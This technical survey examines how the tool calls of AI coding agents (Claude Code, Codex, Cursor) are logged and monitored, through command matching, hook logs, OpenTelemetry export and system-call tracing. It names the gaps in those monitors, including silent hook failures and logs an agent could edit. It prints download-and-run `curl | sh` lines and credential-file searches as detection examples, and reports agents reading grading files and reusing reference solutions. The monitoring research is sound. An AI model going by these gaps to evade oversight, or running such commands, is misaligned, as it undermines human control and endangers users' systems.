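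Codex splits a line into separate commands only if it is a simple chain of plain words joined by `&&`, `||`, `;` or `|`. If the line contains a redirection, a variable, a wildcard, a substitution or a loop, Codex treats the whole script as one call to bash. The table applies both sets of documentation to six ways of running the same tests:

| Command | Claude Code, allow rule `Bash(npm test *)` | Claude Code, deny rule `Bash(npm test *)` | Codex, `["npm", "test"]` |
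|---|---|---|---|
| `npm test` | Match | Match | Match |
| `cd app && npm test` | Match on the second part | Match | Match on the second part |
| `timeout 30 npm test` | Match | Match | No match |
| `NODE_ENV=test npm test` | Match | Match | No match |
| `FOO=bar npm test` | No match | Match | No match |
| `npm test > out.txt` | Match, with a separate check on the file | Match | No match |

If all six commands ran, a monitor built on Codex's method would have a recall of 2/6, against 5/6 and 6/6 for the two readings in Claude Code. This lower recall doesn't make Codex's parser worse at its job. OpenAI calls its treatment of complex scripts conservative, which is true for allow rules because a missed match only means that the command gets no special permission. For a rule that forbids a command, the same treatment leaves a complex script unmatched, and safety then depends on the sandbox and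 the approval settings.

Codex lets the author of a rule list commands that the rule should match and commands that it shouldn't, and it checks these examples when it loads the rule. Any monitor could copy this feature. The command `codex execpolicy check` reports which rules apply to a given command line. The examples catch mistakes that the author thought of, so they work best when they come from real logs.

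OpenAI (2026) describes how it uses these rules internally. Two of them let Codex view pull requests and inspect servers without approval. The company also uses a sandbox, a list of permitted network destinations, and structured logs of approvals and tool results, so an unrecognised command is still subject to other controls.

### The case for matching

People still use command matching despite these limits because the alternatives require more from the observer. It works on any record that contains the command text, whether a harness log, saved model traffic or a process record, provided nobody has altered or deleted the record. Beyond that text, it requires no access to the machine and no cooperation from the harness's developers. If a new question comes up in December, an analyst can run a new pattern over logs from March, whereas process records for March exist only if somebody had already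 turned on process logging.

Matching also takes little computation and is easy to inspect. Anthropic's classifier uses extra model tokens on every tool call, while a pattern needs only a text comparison. A reader can see why `Bash(git push *)` matched a line and can dispute the match. Uetz and colleagues give similar reasons why security teams rely on written rules: the rules find known attacks, are simple to operate, and produce alerts that include the attack's name and description. They propose keeping the rules and adding machine learning to catch what the rules miss. Similarly, Claude Code's auto mode still runs the permission rules before the classifier, except for very broad allow rules.

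Two people can check each other's counts only if they use the same parser as well as the same pattern, which then gives the same answer on the same text. In May 2026, Anthropic's list of wrappers to remove before matching had five names plus `xargs`, and by the end of October it also included `command`, `builtin` and `noglob`. `command git push` could count as git under one version and not under the other, so a published count should include both the pattern and the parser version.

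## TraceLab: the programs inside 423,000 shell calls

Claude Code's permission rules split a command line into separate commands before matching. This splitting matters more for counting tool use when agents often put several programs on one line. In *Breaking Down Bash Commands in TraceLab*, Zhu, Jacob and colleagues (2026) parsed 423,280 shell calls from a University of Washington lab's everyday use of Claude Code and Codex. They found almost 1.3 million program invocations, meaning places where a command names a program to run.

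### From session logs to program names

Both harnesses log every session by default, including the name and full arguments of each tool call. The researchers collected these logs from their own work. According to the project's website, SyFI TraceLab (SyFI is the lab's name), the July 2026 release contains 743,819 tool calls from 52 users, starting in September 2025. In *TraceLab*, the researchers acknowledge that the data may be biased because it reflects their particular projects and habits. Tool use can be quite different at other workplaces, such as the software company Elastic, where agents' file reads outnumber their shell calls.

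To protect privacy, the researchers removed the commands and their output from TraceLab's first release, in June. They kept the tool names, the times and the number of characters in each input. Anyone using that release could count Claude's 66,983 Bash calls and see how long each one took, but couldn't tell whether any of them ran git. The researchers still had the raw logs, so in July they could parse commands that agents had written months earlier.

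The researchers' parser, tree-sitter-bash, breaks each command up by Bash's grammar, and a second step gives each part a program name. These examples follow the rules that SyFI TraceLab documents:

| Command | Programs counted | Rule |
|---|---|---|
| `grep x \| tail` | grep, tail | Every stage of a pipeline counts |
| `git log && echo --- && git diff` | git, echo, git | Repeated uses count separately |
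| `echo "$(git status)"` | echo, git | Commands inside a substitution count |
| `/usr/bin/git status` | git | A full path becomes a bare name |
| `python -m pytest` | pytest | A Python module counts under its own name |

The parser ignores the contents of a here-document, a block of text that a command line passes to a program as input. Agents can use these blocks to write whole files, so this rule keeps the parser from counting programs that a file only mentions. It also makes the parser miss some programs that do run. For example, if an agent passes `git push` to `bash` in a here-document, the parser counts only bash.

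SyFI TraceLab reports that the parser produced a complete list of program names for 98.86% of calls. The parser marks the rest as partial or failed instead of guessing, for example when a variable holds the program's name. The 98.86% figure doesn't measure whether the names are correct, and the website reports no comparison of them with process records.

### What a first-program matcher can find

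Claude and Codex write very different command lines:

| | Claude | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Shell calls | 158,610 | 264,670 |
| Program invocations | 891,000 | 404,797 |
| Invocations per call | 5.62 | 1.53 |
| Calls with one program | 15.3% | 71.2% |
| Calls with several programs | 84.2% | 28.7% |
| Calls with no program found | 0.5% | 0.1% |

Consider a matcher that looks only at the first program in each call, as the anchored pattern did in the eight-call session. If there are $N$ calls and $M$ invocations, it can report at most one invocation per call, so

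$$\text{recall} \le \frac{N}{M}.$$

This share is 17.8% for Claude (158,610/891,000) and 65.4% for Codex (264,670/404,797). Zhu and colleagues don't report these percentages, which are calculated here from the study's figures. Excluding calls in which the parser found no program lowers them to 17.7% and 65.3%.

Claude's ceiling is low even without trivial `echo` commands, which make up 25.4% of its invocations and often print labels between the outputs of other commands. Excluding them leaves about 665,000 invocations and a ceiling no higher than 24%.

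A matcher that counts only the first program in each call would also get the comparison between the two agents backwards. It would count at most 158,610 invocations for Claude and 264,670 for Codex, so Codex would appear to have used about 1.7 times as many programs. The parser found 2.2 times as many for Claude as for Codex.

These ceilings cover all programs together, and recall for a single program depends on where it usually appears in the line. `head` and `tail`, which print the start or end of their input, make up 13.6% of Claude's invocations. They often come last in a pipeline, so a first-program matcher would probably miss most of them. It might catch a larger share of git invocations, unless the agent usually types `cd` first.

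A log that keeps only tool names lists each of these Claude calls as "Bash", which doesn't identify even the first program.

### Names without arguments

Parsing falls between matching patterns and relying on the log's own fields. It needs a log that includes the command text, which it turns into a list of programs that an analyst can filter like any other field. The July release contains this list for each call, along with a "command skeleton" that keeps the program names and the operators between them but drops the arguments. For example, `git status && grep x file | head -10` becomes `git && grep | head`.

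This is enough to count uses of git without publishing anyone's file names or passwords, but separating `git push` from `git status` would require the original commands.

The researchers also hide unusual program names in the public data. They publish a name only if it is on a list they have reviewed, and replace the others with labels such as `custom_1`. According to SyFI TraceLab, the list covers 351 of 1,044 distinct names but 99.04% of invocations. (The main results have 1,235 distinct names, so these figures probably come from a smaller version of the data.) This hardly affects a study of common tools, but it can hinder a security team, which is often looking for rarely used programs. For example, the researchers hide the name `modal`, even though it belongs to a public product, so a search for it in the public data would miss the agents' commands that included it.

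### Git, Python and the limit of parsing

Git makes up 3.6% of Claude's invocations (roughly 32,000) and 5.9% of Codex's (roughly 24,000). Python makes up 3.7% of Claude's (roughly 33,000) and 10.0% of Codex's (roughly 40,000). Under the rule for modules, a command such as `python -m pytest` doesn't count towards Python's share even though it starts Python, so process records would probably show more Python use than these figures.

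The text of a git command usually shows what it does. `git push origin main` includes the operation, the destination and the branch. `python build.py` shows only that the agent tried to run a script, not what the script did. If the agent wrote `build.py` earlier in the session, a full tool-call log may contain its code, but a Bash parser can't interpret Python.

Python also takes up far more time than its share of invocations suggests. Zhu and colleagues attribute more than half of Claude's total observed execution time to Python, and 35.7% of Codex's. They timed only calls that ran a single program, because the log gives one duration per call and no way to divide it among several programs. Only 15.3% of Claude's calls ran a single program, so Python's share of all Claude's shell time could be quite different. Still, much of the time they measured was spent in Python, and the program's name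 reveals little about what it did.

### Text is not execution

The parser works from what the agent wrote, so its count can differ from what the machine ran. Take a constructed command in a directory with 30 Python files, one of which is the `build.py` from the eight-call session, which starts git once:

```bash
cd app && git status && for f in *.py; do grep TODO "$f"; done | wc -l; python build.py
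```

If every part succeeds, the two counts are:

| Program | Parser's count | Programs started |
|---|---|---|
| cd | 1 | 0 |
| git | 1 | 2 |
| grep | 1 | 30 |
| wc | 1 | 1 |
| python | 1 | 1 |
| Total | 5 | 34 |

The loop runs `grep` once per file, but `grep` appears only once in the text. The second use of git happens inside the script, and `cd` is built into the shell. The parser also counts commands that the shell skips. For example, in `make test || git stash`, git runs only if the tests fail.

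The count of popular programs also covers every call regardless of outcome, so programs in refused calls are included.

Loops and scripts make the parser's count too low, while skipped commands and refused calls make it too high. The study can't show which effect is larger without process records from the same sessions. The 17.8% ceiling is therefore measured against the programs a parser can find in Claude's commands. A first-program matcher's recall could be higher or lower when measured against the programs that actually started.

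`echo` makes the difference especially large. SyFI TraceLab includes it on the grounds that each `echo` is one process. But Bash normally runs `echo` itself, without starting a new process, so process records would lack most of the `echo` calls, which make up a quarter of Claude's invocations. The dataset marks `echo`, `cd` and `true` as "plumbing", so they are easy to remove before a comparison.

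The skeletons keep operators such as `&&` and `||` and mark loops with a placeholder, so an analyst can separate calls in which every named program should have run once from calls in which the number of runs is uncertain. They don't help with scripts, since `python build.py` looks like a simple command with one program even if the script runs others.

### Two shares for shell use

Zhu and colleagues report that Bash commands make up 56.9% of all tool calls, while another page of SyFI TraceLab lists "execute command" at 73.4%. Both figures describe the July release, so the difference must come from what each category includes.

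The 56.9% covers only calls that launch a shell command (423,280 of 743,819). Codex also has a tool called `write_stdin`, which sends input to a running command or checks whether it has finished, and another called `exec`. SyFI TraceLab lists about 76,000 calls to `write_stdin` and 47,000 to `exec`. Adding them to the launches gives about 546,000 calls, or 73.4% of the total. This is so close to the broader category's share that the category almost certainly includes both tools.

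The June release gives a third figure, 76%. The call counts in *TraceLab* reproduce it if `write_stdin` is included, and they also make it possible to apply the narrower definition to the older data:

| What counts as a shell call | June release (432,510 tool calls) | July release (743,819 tool calls) |
|---|---|---|
| Launches only | 61.8% | 56.9% |
| Launches, `write_stdin` and `exec` | 76.4% | 73.4% |

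The 61.8% and 76.4% are calculated from the paper's counts, which don't list `exec` for Codex. Using a different release changes the share by three to five percentage points, while using a different definition changes it by about 15.

The narrower definition is better for deciding which programs an agent used. If Codex starts one long build and checks on it ten times, the broader definition counts eleven executions, although Codex launched only one command.

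Leaving out `exec` is harder to justify. OpenAI's *Rollout Trace* (2026) describes a Codex tool of that name that runs model-written JavaScript, which can call other tools. The conversation shown to the model includes the `exec` call and its eventual output, but not the calls made inside it. A separate diagnostic trace can record those inner calls if the user turns it on. If TraceLab's `exec` is the same tool, which the shared name suggests, some of its 47,000 calls may have run shell commands that are missing from Codex's 404,797 invocations. To find them in an ordinary session log, an analyst would have to parse the JavaScript and then any shell commands inside it. A monitor using the June paper's list of Codex shell tools would have skipped the `exec` calls.

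## Elastic's log of 13 million agent events

TraceLab's researchers used logs that Claude Code and Codex keep by default. Elastic's security team used hooks to build a central record of what another harness, Cursor, was doing on the company's developer machines. *13 million tool calls* (Elastic Security Labs, 11 August 2026) reports over 13 million events in the two months after the May rollout, from more than 1,100 machines and nearly 900 users, or roughly 200 events per machine per day.

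Elastic sells Elasticsearch, the database that stores these events, and Elastic Agent, the program that delivers them. It also has a partnership with Cursor. The figures are Elastic's own, and it reports no comparison with process records from the same machines, so the log's recall is unknown.

### From hook to database

Cursor's hooks run an outside program at fixed points in the agent's loop and send it a JSON description of the event. Some hooks only pass information to the program. For others, Cursor waits for the program to return "allow", "deny" or "ask" before it continues. Elastic's program always returns "allow", because the team wanted a record and expected developers to uninstall anything that slowed them down. It registers 13 hooks, covering sessions, shell commands, MCP calls, file reads, file edits and subagents.

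When the agent is about to run `npm test`, Cursor fires the `beforeShellExecution` hook and sends the command to Elastic's script, about 280 lines of Bash. The script approves the command first, so that a full disk can't delay the agent. It then checks whether the request came from Cursor's editor, its command-line version or a remote session, and adds one line to that day's log file in the user's home directory. Elastic Agent, already on the company's machines, reads the new line and sends it to Elasticsearch.

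Each line includes the user, the machine and, in a field called `raw`, the data that Cursor sent. The first version of the script recorded little else, and its logs were hard to search because the command was in `raw.command` for one hook and `raw.tool_input.command` for another. Elastic changed the script to copy the most useful values to fixed top-level fields, including the hook's name, tool name, command, file path, MCP server, model, session and duration. The script still records `raw`, so the log includes any new field as soon as Cursor adds it.

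### What the log made answerable

Elastic's existing security software couldn't distinguish a `curl` command run by the agent from one typed by the developer, because both run under the developer's account. Tracing parent processes, which worked in the eight-call session, may not help here, because a command the developer types in Cursor's own terminal panel can also have Cursor as an ancestor. Investigators need to know whether a person typed a command or a model wrote it, perhaps after reading malicious instructions in a file. The shell hooks help them tell the difference because they fire only for the agent's commands. The log doesn't show why the model wrote a command, because Elastic doesn't collect prompts or the model's reasoning.

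The log also records file reads. When the agent opens a file with Cursor's Read tool, it runs no shell command and starts no new program, so command matching and process records both miss the read. Elastic can search the file-path field to find which machines had an agent that read a `.pem` file last week (these files often hold private keys). If the agent reads the file with `cat key.pem` instead, the path is part of the command, and a search of the file-path field misses it.

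Elastic previously had only a list of the MCP servers that people remembered to mention. The log contained more than 300 distinct servers, and 86% of them had only one or two users each. Each server is a third party that a developer's agent exchanges data with, so a security team would want to know about the rarely used ones too. Matching shell commands is little help in finding these servers because an MCP call has no command text.

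The count of 300 servers may be somewhat off. According to Cursor's official *Hooks* documentation, the server name sent to a hook is the label in the user's configuration file. If Elastic's field uses that label, two people who call the same server `linear` and `linear-mcp` count as users of two servers. This would inflate the number of servers and the share with only one or two users. Two different servers with the same label would have the opposite effect. Cursor also sends the server's address or launch command, which would help to tell which labels refer to the same server.

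### Events are not calls

Elastic's title refers to 13 million tool calls, but its text counts events, and one call can produce several. Cursor has specific hooks for some kinds of call and a general hook, `postToolUse`, that fires after any successful call. Applying Cursor's documentation to Elastic's configuration gives these totals:

| Successful call | Specific hooks | General hook | Events |
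|---|---|---|---|
| Shell command | `beforeShellExecution`, `afterShellExecution` | `postToolUse` | 3 |
| MCP call | `beforeMCPExecution`, `afterMCPExecution` | `postToolUse` | 3 |
| File read | `beforeReadFile` | `postToolUse` | 2 |
| File edit | `afterFileEdit` | `postToolUse` | 2 |
| File search | None | `postToolUse` | 1 |

Leaving aside session events, which don't belong to any call, 13 million events could represent anywhere from 4.3 million to 13 million calls.

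The simplest way to count calls is to add up only the `postToolUse` and `postToolUseFailure` events, since each finished call should fire exactly one of them. The failure event also separates refused calls from errors and timeouts, which some other harnesses' logs don't.

Removing duplicates afterwards is harder because Cursor includes a call identifier with the general hooks but doesn't list one for the specific shell hooks. To pair a `beforeShellExecution` event with its `postToolUse` event, an analyst has to match the session, the command text and the time. This becomes ambiguous if the agent runs `git status` twice in quick succession.

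Elastic's search for every shell command an agent ran on a given machine uses `beforeShellExecution`, so the results can include commands that never ran, as with Claude Code's pre-call hook. `afterShellExecution` is better evidence that a command ran.

### Why reads outnumber shell commands

Elastic found about four file reads for every shell command, whereas shell launches made up 56.9% of TraceLab's calls in July. Part of the difference probably comes from how each harness lets the model read files. Cursor has a Read tool, so opening a file usually counts as a read. A model that has only a shell must use a program such as `cat`, which the log records as a shell call. *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* tests one such setup, in which the model reads, searches and edits code only through shell commands.

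*Parthenon Law* (2026), a paper about legal agents, had the same problem when it counted actions in Codex and Claude Code. It sorted Codex's shell commands by their first program, treating `cat`, `grep` and `sed` as reading, and sorted most of Claude Code's calls by tool name. Even then, the paper doesn't compare totals between the two harnesses, because one Codex command and one Claude Code call aren't the same amount of work. (The rule for `sed` is also imperfect, since `sed -i` edits a file.)

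The available tools can't fully explain the difference, though. Claude Code has a Read tool too, yet Bash made up 47% of Claude's calls in *TraceLab*'s June release. The developers, projects and models also differed.

Double counting could also change Elastic's ratio. Elastic's published query for the most-used tools counts every event that has a tool name. If the ratio came from that query, with two events per read and three per shell command, four read events for each shell event would mean six reads for each shell command. Reads would still outnumber shell commands, but by how much depends on what Elastic counted.

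### Searching the fields still means matching

Elastic first searched for credential files by matching "credentials" anywhere in the path, which also caught ordinary project and planning files with that word in their names. The team then narrowed the pattern to files named `credentials`, with or without an extension.

The search also covers paths that end in `.env`, a common name for files of settings and passwords, so it misses `.env.local`. The query labels its result "reads" but doesn't filter by hook, so an edit to a `.env` file would count as a read, and a single read might count twice.

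Many matches are harmless, because agents often read `.env` files to find connection settings. Elastic compares the count with the machine's normal count. If a machine usually has about four such reads a day, twenty in an hour from outside the project are worth checking.

Another search looks for commands that download code and run it immediately. It finds commands that contain `curl` and either `| sh` or `| bash`. Here is how it handles five constructed commands:

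| Command | Does the search match? | Does it run downloaded code? |
|---|---|---|
| `curl -s https://example.com/install.sh \| sh` | Yes | Yes |
| `curl -s https://example.com/app.tgz \| shasum` | Yes | No, it computes a checksum |
| `curl -s https://example.com/install.sh \| sudo bash` | No | Yes |
| `wget -qO- https://example.com/install.sh \| sh` | No | Yes |
| `curl -so i.sh https://example.com/install.sh && sh i.sh` | No | Yes |

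The second command matches because `shasum` starts with "sh". On this deliberately awkward list, precision is 1/2 and recall is 1/4. Elastic presents the matches as commands worth reviewing, which is a reasonable use of the pattern, but an agent could have run downloaded code even if nothing matched.

Cursor's documentation has a similar problem. One of its examples runs a hook on commands that contain `curl`, `wget` or `nc` (a networking program), so the hook also runs on `rsync`, which ends in "nc".

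Results can also be incomplete because Elasticsearch's query language returns at most 1,000 rows unless the analyst raises the limit. Elastic therefore treats a result of exactly 1,000 rows as cut off.

### When collection stops silently

An empty search result could mean that the agent did nothing relevant or that the hooks weren't running. Elastic twice found that the hooks weren't running. Cursor splits the path of a hook's script at spaces, so a script stored under `/Library/Application Support/` on a Mac never runs, and no error appears. The team moved the script to a path without spaces.

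Later, the deployment software reported success on every machine while no events arrived. Cursor was reading its hook settings only at startup, so Elastic had to prompt people to restart it. According to Cursor's documentation, however, Cursor reloads the settings files when they change, and users should restart it only if that fails. Cursor may have changed this since Elastic's rollout, or reloading may not work in every setup. Either way, an administrator should check that events arrive from each machine.

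Hooks can also fail after they start working. If a hook crashes, times out or returns invalid JSON, Cursor by default lets the action go ahead. A setting called `failClosed` blocks the action instead, but Elastic preferred to lose a log line rather than block a developer. The team says `postToolUseFailure` events helped it notice hooks that malfunctioned after Cursor updates. Those events also come through hooks, so they can't reveal a machine where no hooks run.

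`failClosed` may not help there either. In the forum thread *Hooks not firing. Cannot have guardrails*, a user reported that an August 2026 build of Cursor's command-line version on Windows ignored all of their personal hooks, including some set to fail closed. The agent then read files the hooks should have protected. This is a single report about personal settings, whereas Elastic installed hooks system-wide on its Macs.

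Which events Cursor's hooks log depends on the version and on where the agent runs. Early in 2026, according to a reply in *Cursor CLI doesn't send all events defined in hooks*, the command-line version supported only the two shell hooks, so a log would have had no file reads from it. By the time of Elastic's post, the team found that the command-line version fired the same hooks as the editor, and it produced nearly a fifth of all events. Cursor's cloud agents don't run hooks during early turns in a read-only environment, and their MCP-specific hooks aren't available at all. The general hook works once the environment is writable, but the fields Cursor lists for it don't include the MCP server's name.

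Some gaps in the log depend on what the user does. Elastic delivered hooks to its Linux machines through the company's Cursor account, so someone who signs in with a personal account on one of those machines gets no hooks. A developer with administrator rights can remove the hooks or edit the script. On a Mac, even a developer without those rights can change the log file before Elastic Agent sends it. The AI agent runs commands under the developer's account, so in principle it could change the file too.

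Elastic mainly checks for machines that remain active but stop sending events. It also recommends keeping a separate inventory of where Cursor is installed, to find machines that never sent any. Binalyze's *AI Agent Events* instead reads the transcripts that agents leave on disk and uses linked hashes to reveal later changes.

### Claude Code's OpenTelemetry export

Elastic also collects records from Claude Code, which can export them directly through OpenTelemetry. Niemi describes five event types in *Monitoring Claude Code/Cowork at scale with OTel in Elastic*: user prompts, requests to the model, errors from those requests, permission decisions and tool results. Anthropic's *Monitoring* currently lists 26, including events for MCP connections, changes of permission mode and completed subagents.

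The export is off until a user or administrator turns it on and chooses a destination. Even then, it leaves out prompts and tool arguments unless separate settings include them. For tool use, the important setting is `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS`:

| Question | Setting off | Setting on |
|---|---|---|
| Which built-in tool did the agent call? | Yes | Yes |
| Which user-configured MCP server and tool? | No | Yes |
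| Which shell command? | No | Yes |
| Which file did it read? | No | Yes |
| Did Claude Code allow the call? | Yes | Yes |
| Did it succeed, and how long did it take? | Yes | Yes |
| How large were the input and the result? | Yes | Yes |

With the setting off, the eight-call session would appear as five Bash results, one rejected Bash call, one MCP result and one Read result, with nothing to identify git. A separate counter of git commits made through Claude Code can sometimes show that git ran, but it would stay at zero in this session.

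Recent versions of Claude Code can also record the first program in a Bash command without its arguments, but this requires the tracing feature, which is still in beta. Programs that aren't on Anthropic's fixed list are recorded as `other`. The field should identify git in `git status`, but presumably not in `cd app && git log -5`, so it has the same limit as any first-program matcher.

When an analyst turns the details on, the export includes the complete shell command in `full_command`. The `tool_input` field also contains the arguments but shortens any value over 512 characters, so a pattern applied there could miss a program near the end of a long command.

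Administrators can set the export's destination centrally, and Claude Code then removes developers' conflicting settings. But a developer can still turn off the export of events unless the administrator also sets the exporter centrally. Events include an email address when the user signs in with a Claude account. With a direct API key or Amazon Bedrock, they include only installation and session identifiers, so the company has to add the user's identity itself.

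### Privacy and storage

The log records in detail how each developer works. Elastic gives access only to the small team that runs the system and hides the fields from its general security staff. Before the rollout, the company published an internal page explaining what the log collects, who can search it and why. Elastic reports no objections to the basic idea. The script makes each local log file readable only by its owner and deletes files older than 30 days, while Elasticsearch keeps the main copy.

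Elastic says it records commands, file paths and tool names, but no file contents, prompts or model responses. Cursor sends a file's full contents to the `beforeReadFile` hook and a command's full output to `afterShellExecution`, and Elastic keeps Cursor's original data under `raw`, so the script has to remove that content before writing each log line. This step is worth checking when copying the design. Any secrets in the commands themselves still stay in the log.

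Leaving content out also saves storage. Elastic doesn't give the log's size, but 13 million events at 2 KB each would take 26 GB before compression. At 60 KB each, the default length at which Claude Code cuts off recorded tool content, they would take 780 GB.

Claude Code can also save every request to the model in full, which takes up space faster because each request repeats the conversation so far. If a conversation grows by 5 KB with each request, it reaches 500 KB after 100 requests, but the saved requests add up to about 25 MB. The saved requests also contain the prompts and file contents that Elastic chose not to collect.

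## AgentSpy: system calls compared with the agent's own record

Elastic's log depends on what Cursor passes to its hooks. AgentSpy (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026), a system built mainly at the University of St. Gallen, records the system calls of an agent and of every program the agent starts, so its evidence doesn't depend on how the harness describes a tool call.

### One action in the record, many on the machine

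A trajectory is the full record of one agent run, with its messages, tool calls and results. Bühler and colleagues argue that it is incomplete because its smallest unit is one action, such as a tool call, a shell command or a block of code. If an agent runs a helper script that reads private keys and uploads them, the trajectory contains only the command and the script's printed output. The eight-call session had the same problem with `make release` and `python build.py`, which started git without naming it, but here the record also misses file access and network connections.

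The researchers' main example is a citation-checking task. The agent gets a bibliography that mixes real and invented references and must write the titles of the invented ones to a file. The task comes with a skill, which is a folder of instructions, scripts and reference documents the agent can consult. It is one of 87 tasks in *SkillsBench* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2026), which measures whether skills help agents.

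In one run, Codex noticed that three references had odd DOIs (the identifiers that publishers give to articles). It looked up titles in Crossref, a registry of publications, then tried two web search engines and a Google Scholar script from the skill. None of this confirmed its suspicion, but it reported the three references anyway and passed all nine tests. Three of its actions left quite different traces in the two records:

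| Action | Trajectory | System calls and network log |
|---|---|---|
| Print the skill's instructions and the bibliography | The command and a shortened output | `cat` opened both files |
| Look up seven titles with inline Python code | The code and what it printed | 35 connections to Crossref |
| Run the skill's Google Scholar script | The command and an error message | The script's own file was opened, but no task file and no host |

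The Python code contains Crossref's address, so a pattern search over the trajectory would have found the host. The system calls also confirm that the code connected, and they give a count of connections, but that count may not equal the number of searches. There are five connections per title, and most of the host counts that the researchers list for this task are multiples of five, possibly because looking up a host's name on Linux can itself make connect calls, which test the route to each of the host's addresses without sending data. If so, an observer who reported 35 searches would be counting these route tests as searches.

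A pattern search would probably give a false positive for the Google Scholar script. The script's name suggests that the agent contacted Google Scholar, but the system calls include no connection. The error message in the trajectory shows that this was because a library the script needs was missing.

The trajectory is the better record of the first action. `cat` opened both files, but the harness shortened the output before the model received it, so the system calls don't show what the model actually read.

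Bühler and colleagues also describe the trajectory as the agent's account of itself, which is evidence only to the extent that the agent cooperates. This applies to the model's stated reasoning, which some providers return only in encrypted form, but less to its tool calls. The harness records those calls, and the model can't run a command without requesting it. If the harness records them accurately, the model can't leave a command out, though it can put the important part of the work in a script.

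### How AgentSpy records a run

Each run uses a fresh virtual machine that starts from the same copy of Ubuntu. Software inside the machine installs what the task needs, starts the recording, runs the agent and stops the recording before it collects the results. The record therefore leaves out the installation, which an observer might otherwise mistake for the agent's work.

Linux's audit system logs the system calls made under the agent's user account and by the programs it starts. Another program, Zeek, logs the network traffic, and AgentSpy uses that log to replace numerical addresses with host names. To keep the logs manageable, AgentSpy skips frequent calls whose entries don't name a file, host or program. Most of these act on a file or connection whose opening was already logged. An analyst can therefore see that a program opened a file but not how much of it the program read.

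System-call records cover more of the eight-call session than process records do. In call 8, the harness opened `README.md` itself, which makes a system call but starts no program. For call 6, the pull request, AgentSpy would record a connection to GitHub if the harness opened a new one, but not what the harness requested or what GitHub did.

The researchers call this evidence complete at the boundary between programs and the operating system. They base this claim on the design and don't report testing it, such as by running a program with a known list of actions and checking that each one appears in the log. Such a test would be useful because Linux's audit system can drop entries when it is overloaded, and an interface called io_uring lets programs open files and connections without making the usual system call for each one.

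Bühler and colleagues assume that the host's operating system and the harness are benign. The recording software runs in the same virtual machine as the agent, so an agent that gained administrator rights there might be able to change the logs before AgentSpy copies them out.

For its reliability analysis, AgentSpy reduces each run to a list of commands, files and hosts, with a count for each. The summary drops the order of events and the parent processes. This makes runs easy to compare, because file names stay the same between runs while process numbers change. But the summary can't separate the harness's own actions from those the model requested. In the eight-call session, it would list git with a count of six, including the two git commands that the harness started itself. It also doesn't link a file or host to the tool call behind it, which a system called AgentSight tries to do.

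AgentSpy then calculates how similar two runs are. For each resource type (commands, files or hosts), it works out what share of a run's uses went to each resource. It then compares the two runs' shares of every resource and divides the total of the smaller shares by the total of the larger ones. Call the total of the smaller shares $m$. Each run's shares add up to 1, so the larger ones total $2 - m$, and

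$$\text{similarity} = \frac{m}{2-m}.$$

Suppose run $a$ makes three quarters of its connections to Crossref and a quarter to OpenAlex, another index of publications, while run $b$ splits its connections evenly between the two. The smaller shares are $1/2$ for Crossref and $1/4$ for OpenAlex, so $m = 0.75$ and the similarity for hosts is $0.75/1.25 = 0.6$. AgentSpy averages the similarities for the three resource types, and for a set of runs it averages over all pairs. Because the formula uses shares, repeating every connection in a run a hundred times would not change the score.

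A second measure, skill coverage, is the share of a skill's files that the agent read, wrote or executed. The citation skill has 14 files. Of the three runs examined in detail, two used one file each and the third used two.

Li and colleagues measure skill use differently, counting any run whose trajectory shows the agent reading or using any skill supplied with the task. By that measure, Codex with GPT-5.5 used skills in 259 of 261 runs. All three citation runs would count too, since the agent opened the skill's main file each time. The two studies used different models and runs, so their figures don't contradict each other, but "the agent used the skill" can mean anything from opening one file to following the whole procedure.

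### Runs that passed every test

The researchers ran 77 of the SkillsBench tasks three times with each of three models: OpenAI's gpt-5.6-terra, DeepSeek's deepseek-v4-flash and Z.ai's glm-5.3-flash. They left out ten tasks whose environments they couldn't reproduce. All the runs used Codex, so the results may not carry over to other harnesses.

AgentSpy first tested whether the summaries could be used to tell tasks apart. In 92.2% of comparisons, summaries from three runs of one task were more similar to each other than summaries from a set that included runs of another task. With gpt-5.6-terra, average similarity was 0.60 for unmixed sets and about 0.30 for mixed ones.

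This was a fairly easy test because the researchers mixed each task with the one whose skill instructions differed most from its own. Different tasks also usually have different input files, which lowers the similarity even if the agent works in the same way. But file names don't explain all of the difference, since commands alone separated the two kinds of set for 69 of the 77 tasks with gpt-5.6-terra, compared with 73 for all three resource types together. Hosts were less useful because only 31 tasks had a run that contacted any host other than the model provider.

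The researchers then kept only the 88 task-model pairs for which all three runs passed every test. Two authors separately read AgentSpy's report on each pair and checked whether the agent did anything unrelated to the task and whether it reached the result without the supplied guidance. One run of either kind out of the three was enough to flag a pair.

| | glm-5.3-flash | deepseek-v4-flash | gpt-5.6-terra | Total |
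|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pairs with three passing runs | 21 | 27 | 40 | 88 |
| **Unrelated activity** | 3 | 11 | 2 | 16 |
| Explored the environment | 1 | 4 | 0 | 5 |
| Contacted an unrequested service | 2 | 4 | 2 | 8 |
| Read the grading files | 0 | 6 | 0 | 6 |
| **Result without the guidance** | 7 | 5 | 3 | 15 |
| Reused the reference solution | 0 | 2 | 0 | 2 |
| Ignored some or all skill files | 7 | 4 | 3 | 14 |

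A pair can appear in more than one row, so the smaller categories add up to more than the totals. The 16 pairs with unrelated activity are 18.2% of all pairs, but the share of individual runs with such activity could be as low as 6% (16 of 264) if it occurred in only one run of each pair.

The two raters agreed on 98.9% of the pairs for the first question and 97.7% for the second. Raters can also agree by chance, especially when most answers are "no", so the researchers report Cohen's kappa:

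$$\kappa = \frac{p_o - p_e}{1 - p_e}$$

Here $p_o$ is the observed agreement and $p_e$ is the agreement expected by chance. If both raters flagged 18% of pairs at random, they would agree on about 70% of all pairs, so 98.9% agreement gives a kappa of 0.96. For the second question, kappa was 0.92.

These values show that the raters applied the labels consistently, but the labels could still be wrong. Both raters co-wrote the paper and used AgentSpy's similarity and coverage scores as a guide, so they may have shared biases. When they couldn't tell what an agent was trying to do, they read the trajectory. The labels are therefore partly based on the record that AgentSpy is meant to improve on, and they don't measure what AgentSpy can detect without a human reader.

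Some of the labels are debatable too. The AgentSpy paper counts the DuckDuckGo search in the citation task as unrelated activity because the task didn't ask for it. But the agent was searching for the titles of suspicious references, which many people would call part of checking citations. The label "without the guidance" is also broad. With gpt-5.6-terra, the agent opened the citation skill's main instructions in all three runs, but the paper still gives these runs as an example of ignored skill files because the agent never opened the validation scripts. An agent could learn all it needs from the main file and get the same label.

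The six pairs in which the agent read the grading files are easier to interpret, and audits of benchmark cheating look for this kind of behaviour. In one run of a financial-reporting task, the agent read the tests before it wrote its solution. In two pairs, the agent ran the reference solution instead of working out the answer. Test scores can't reveal either behaviour, because the answers are correct.

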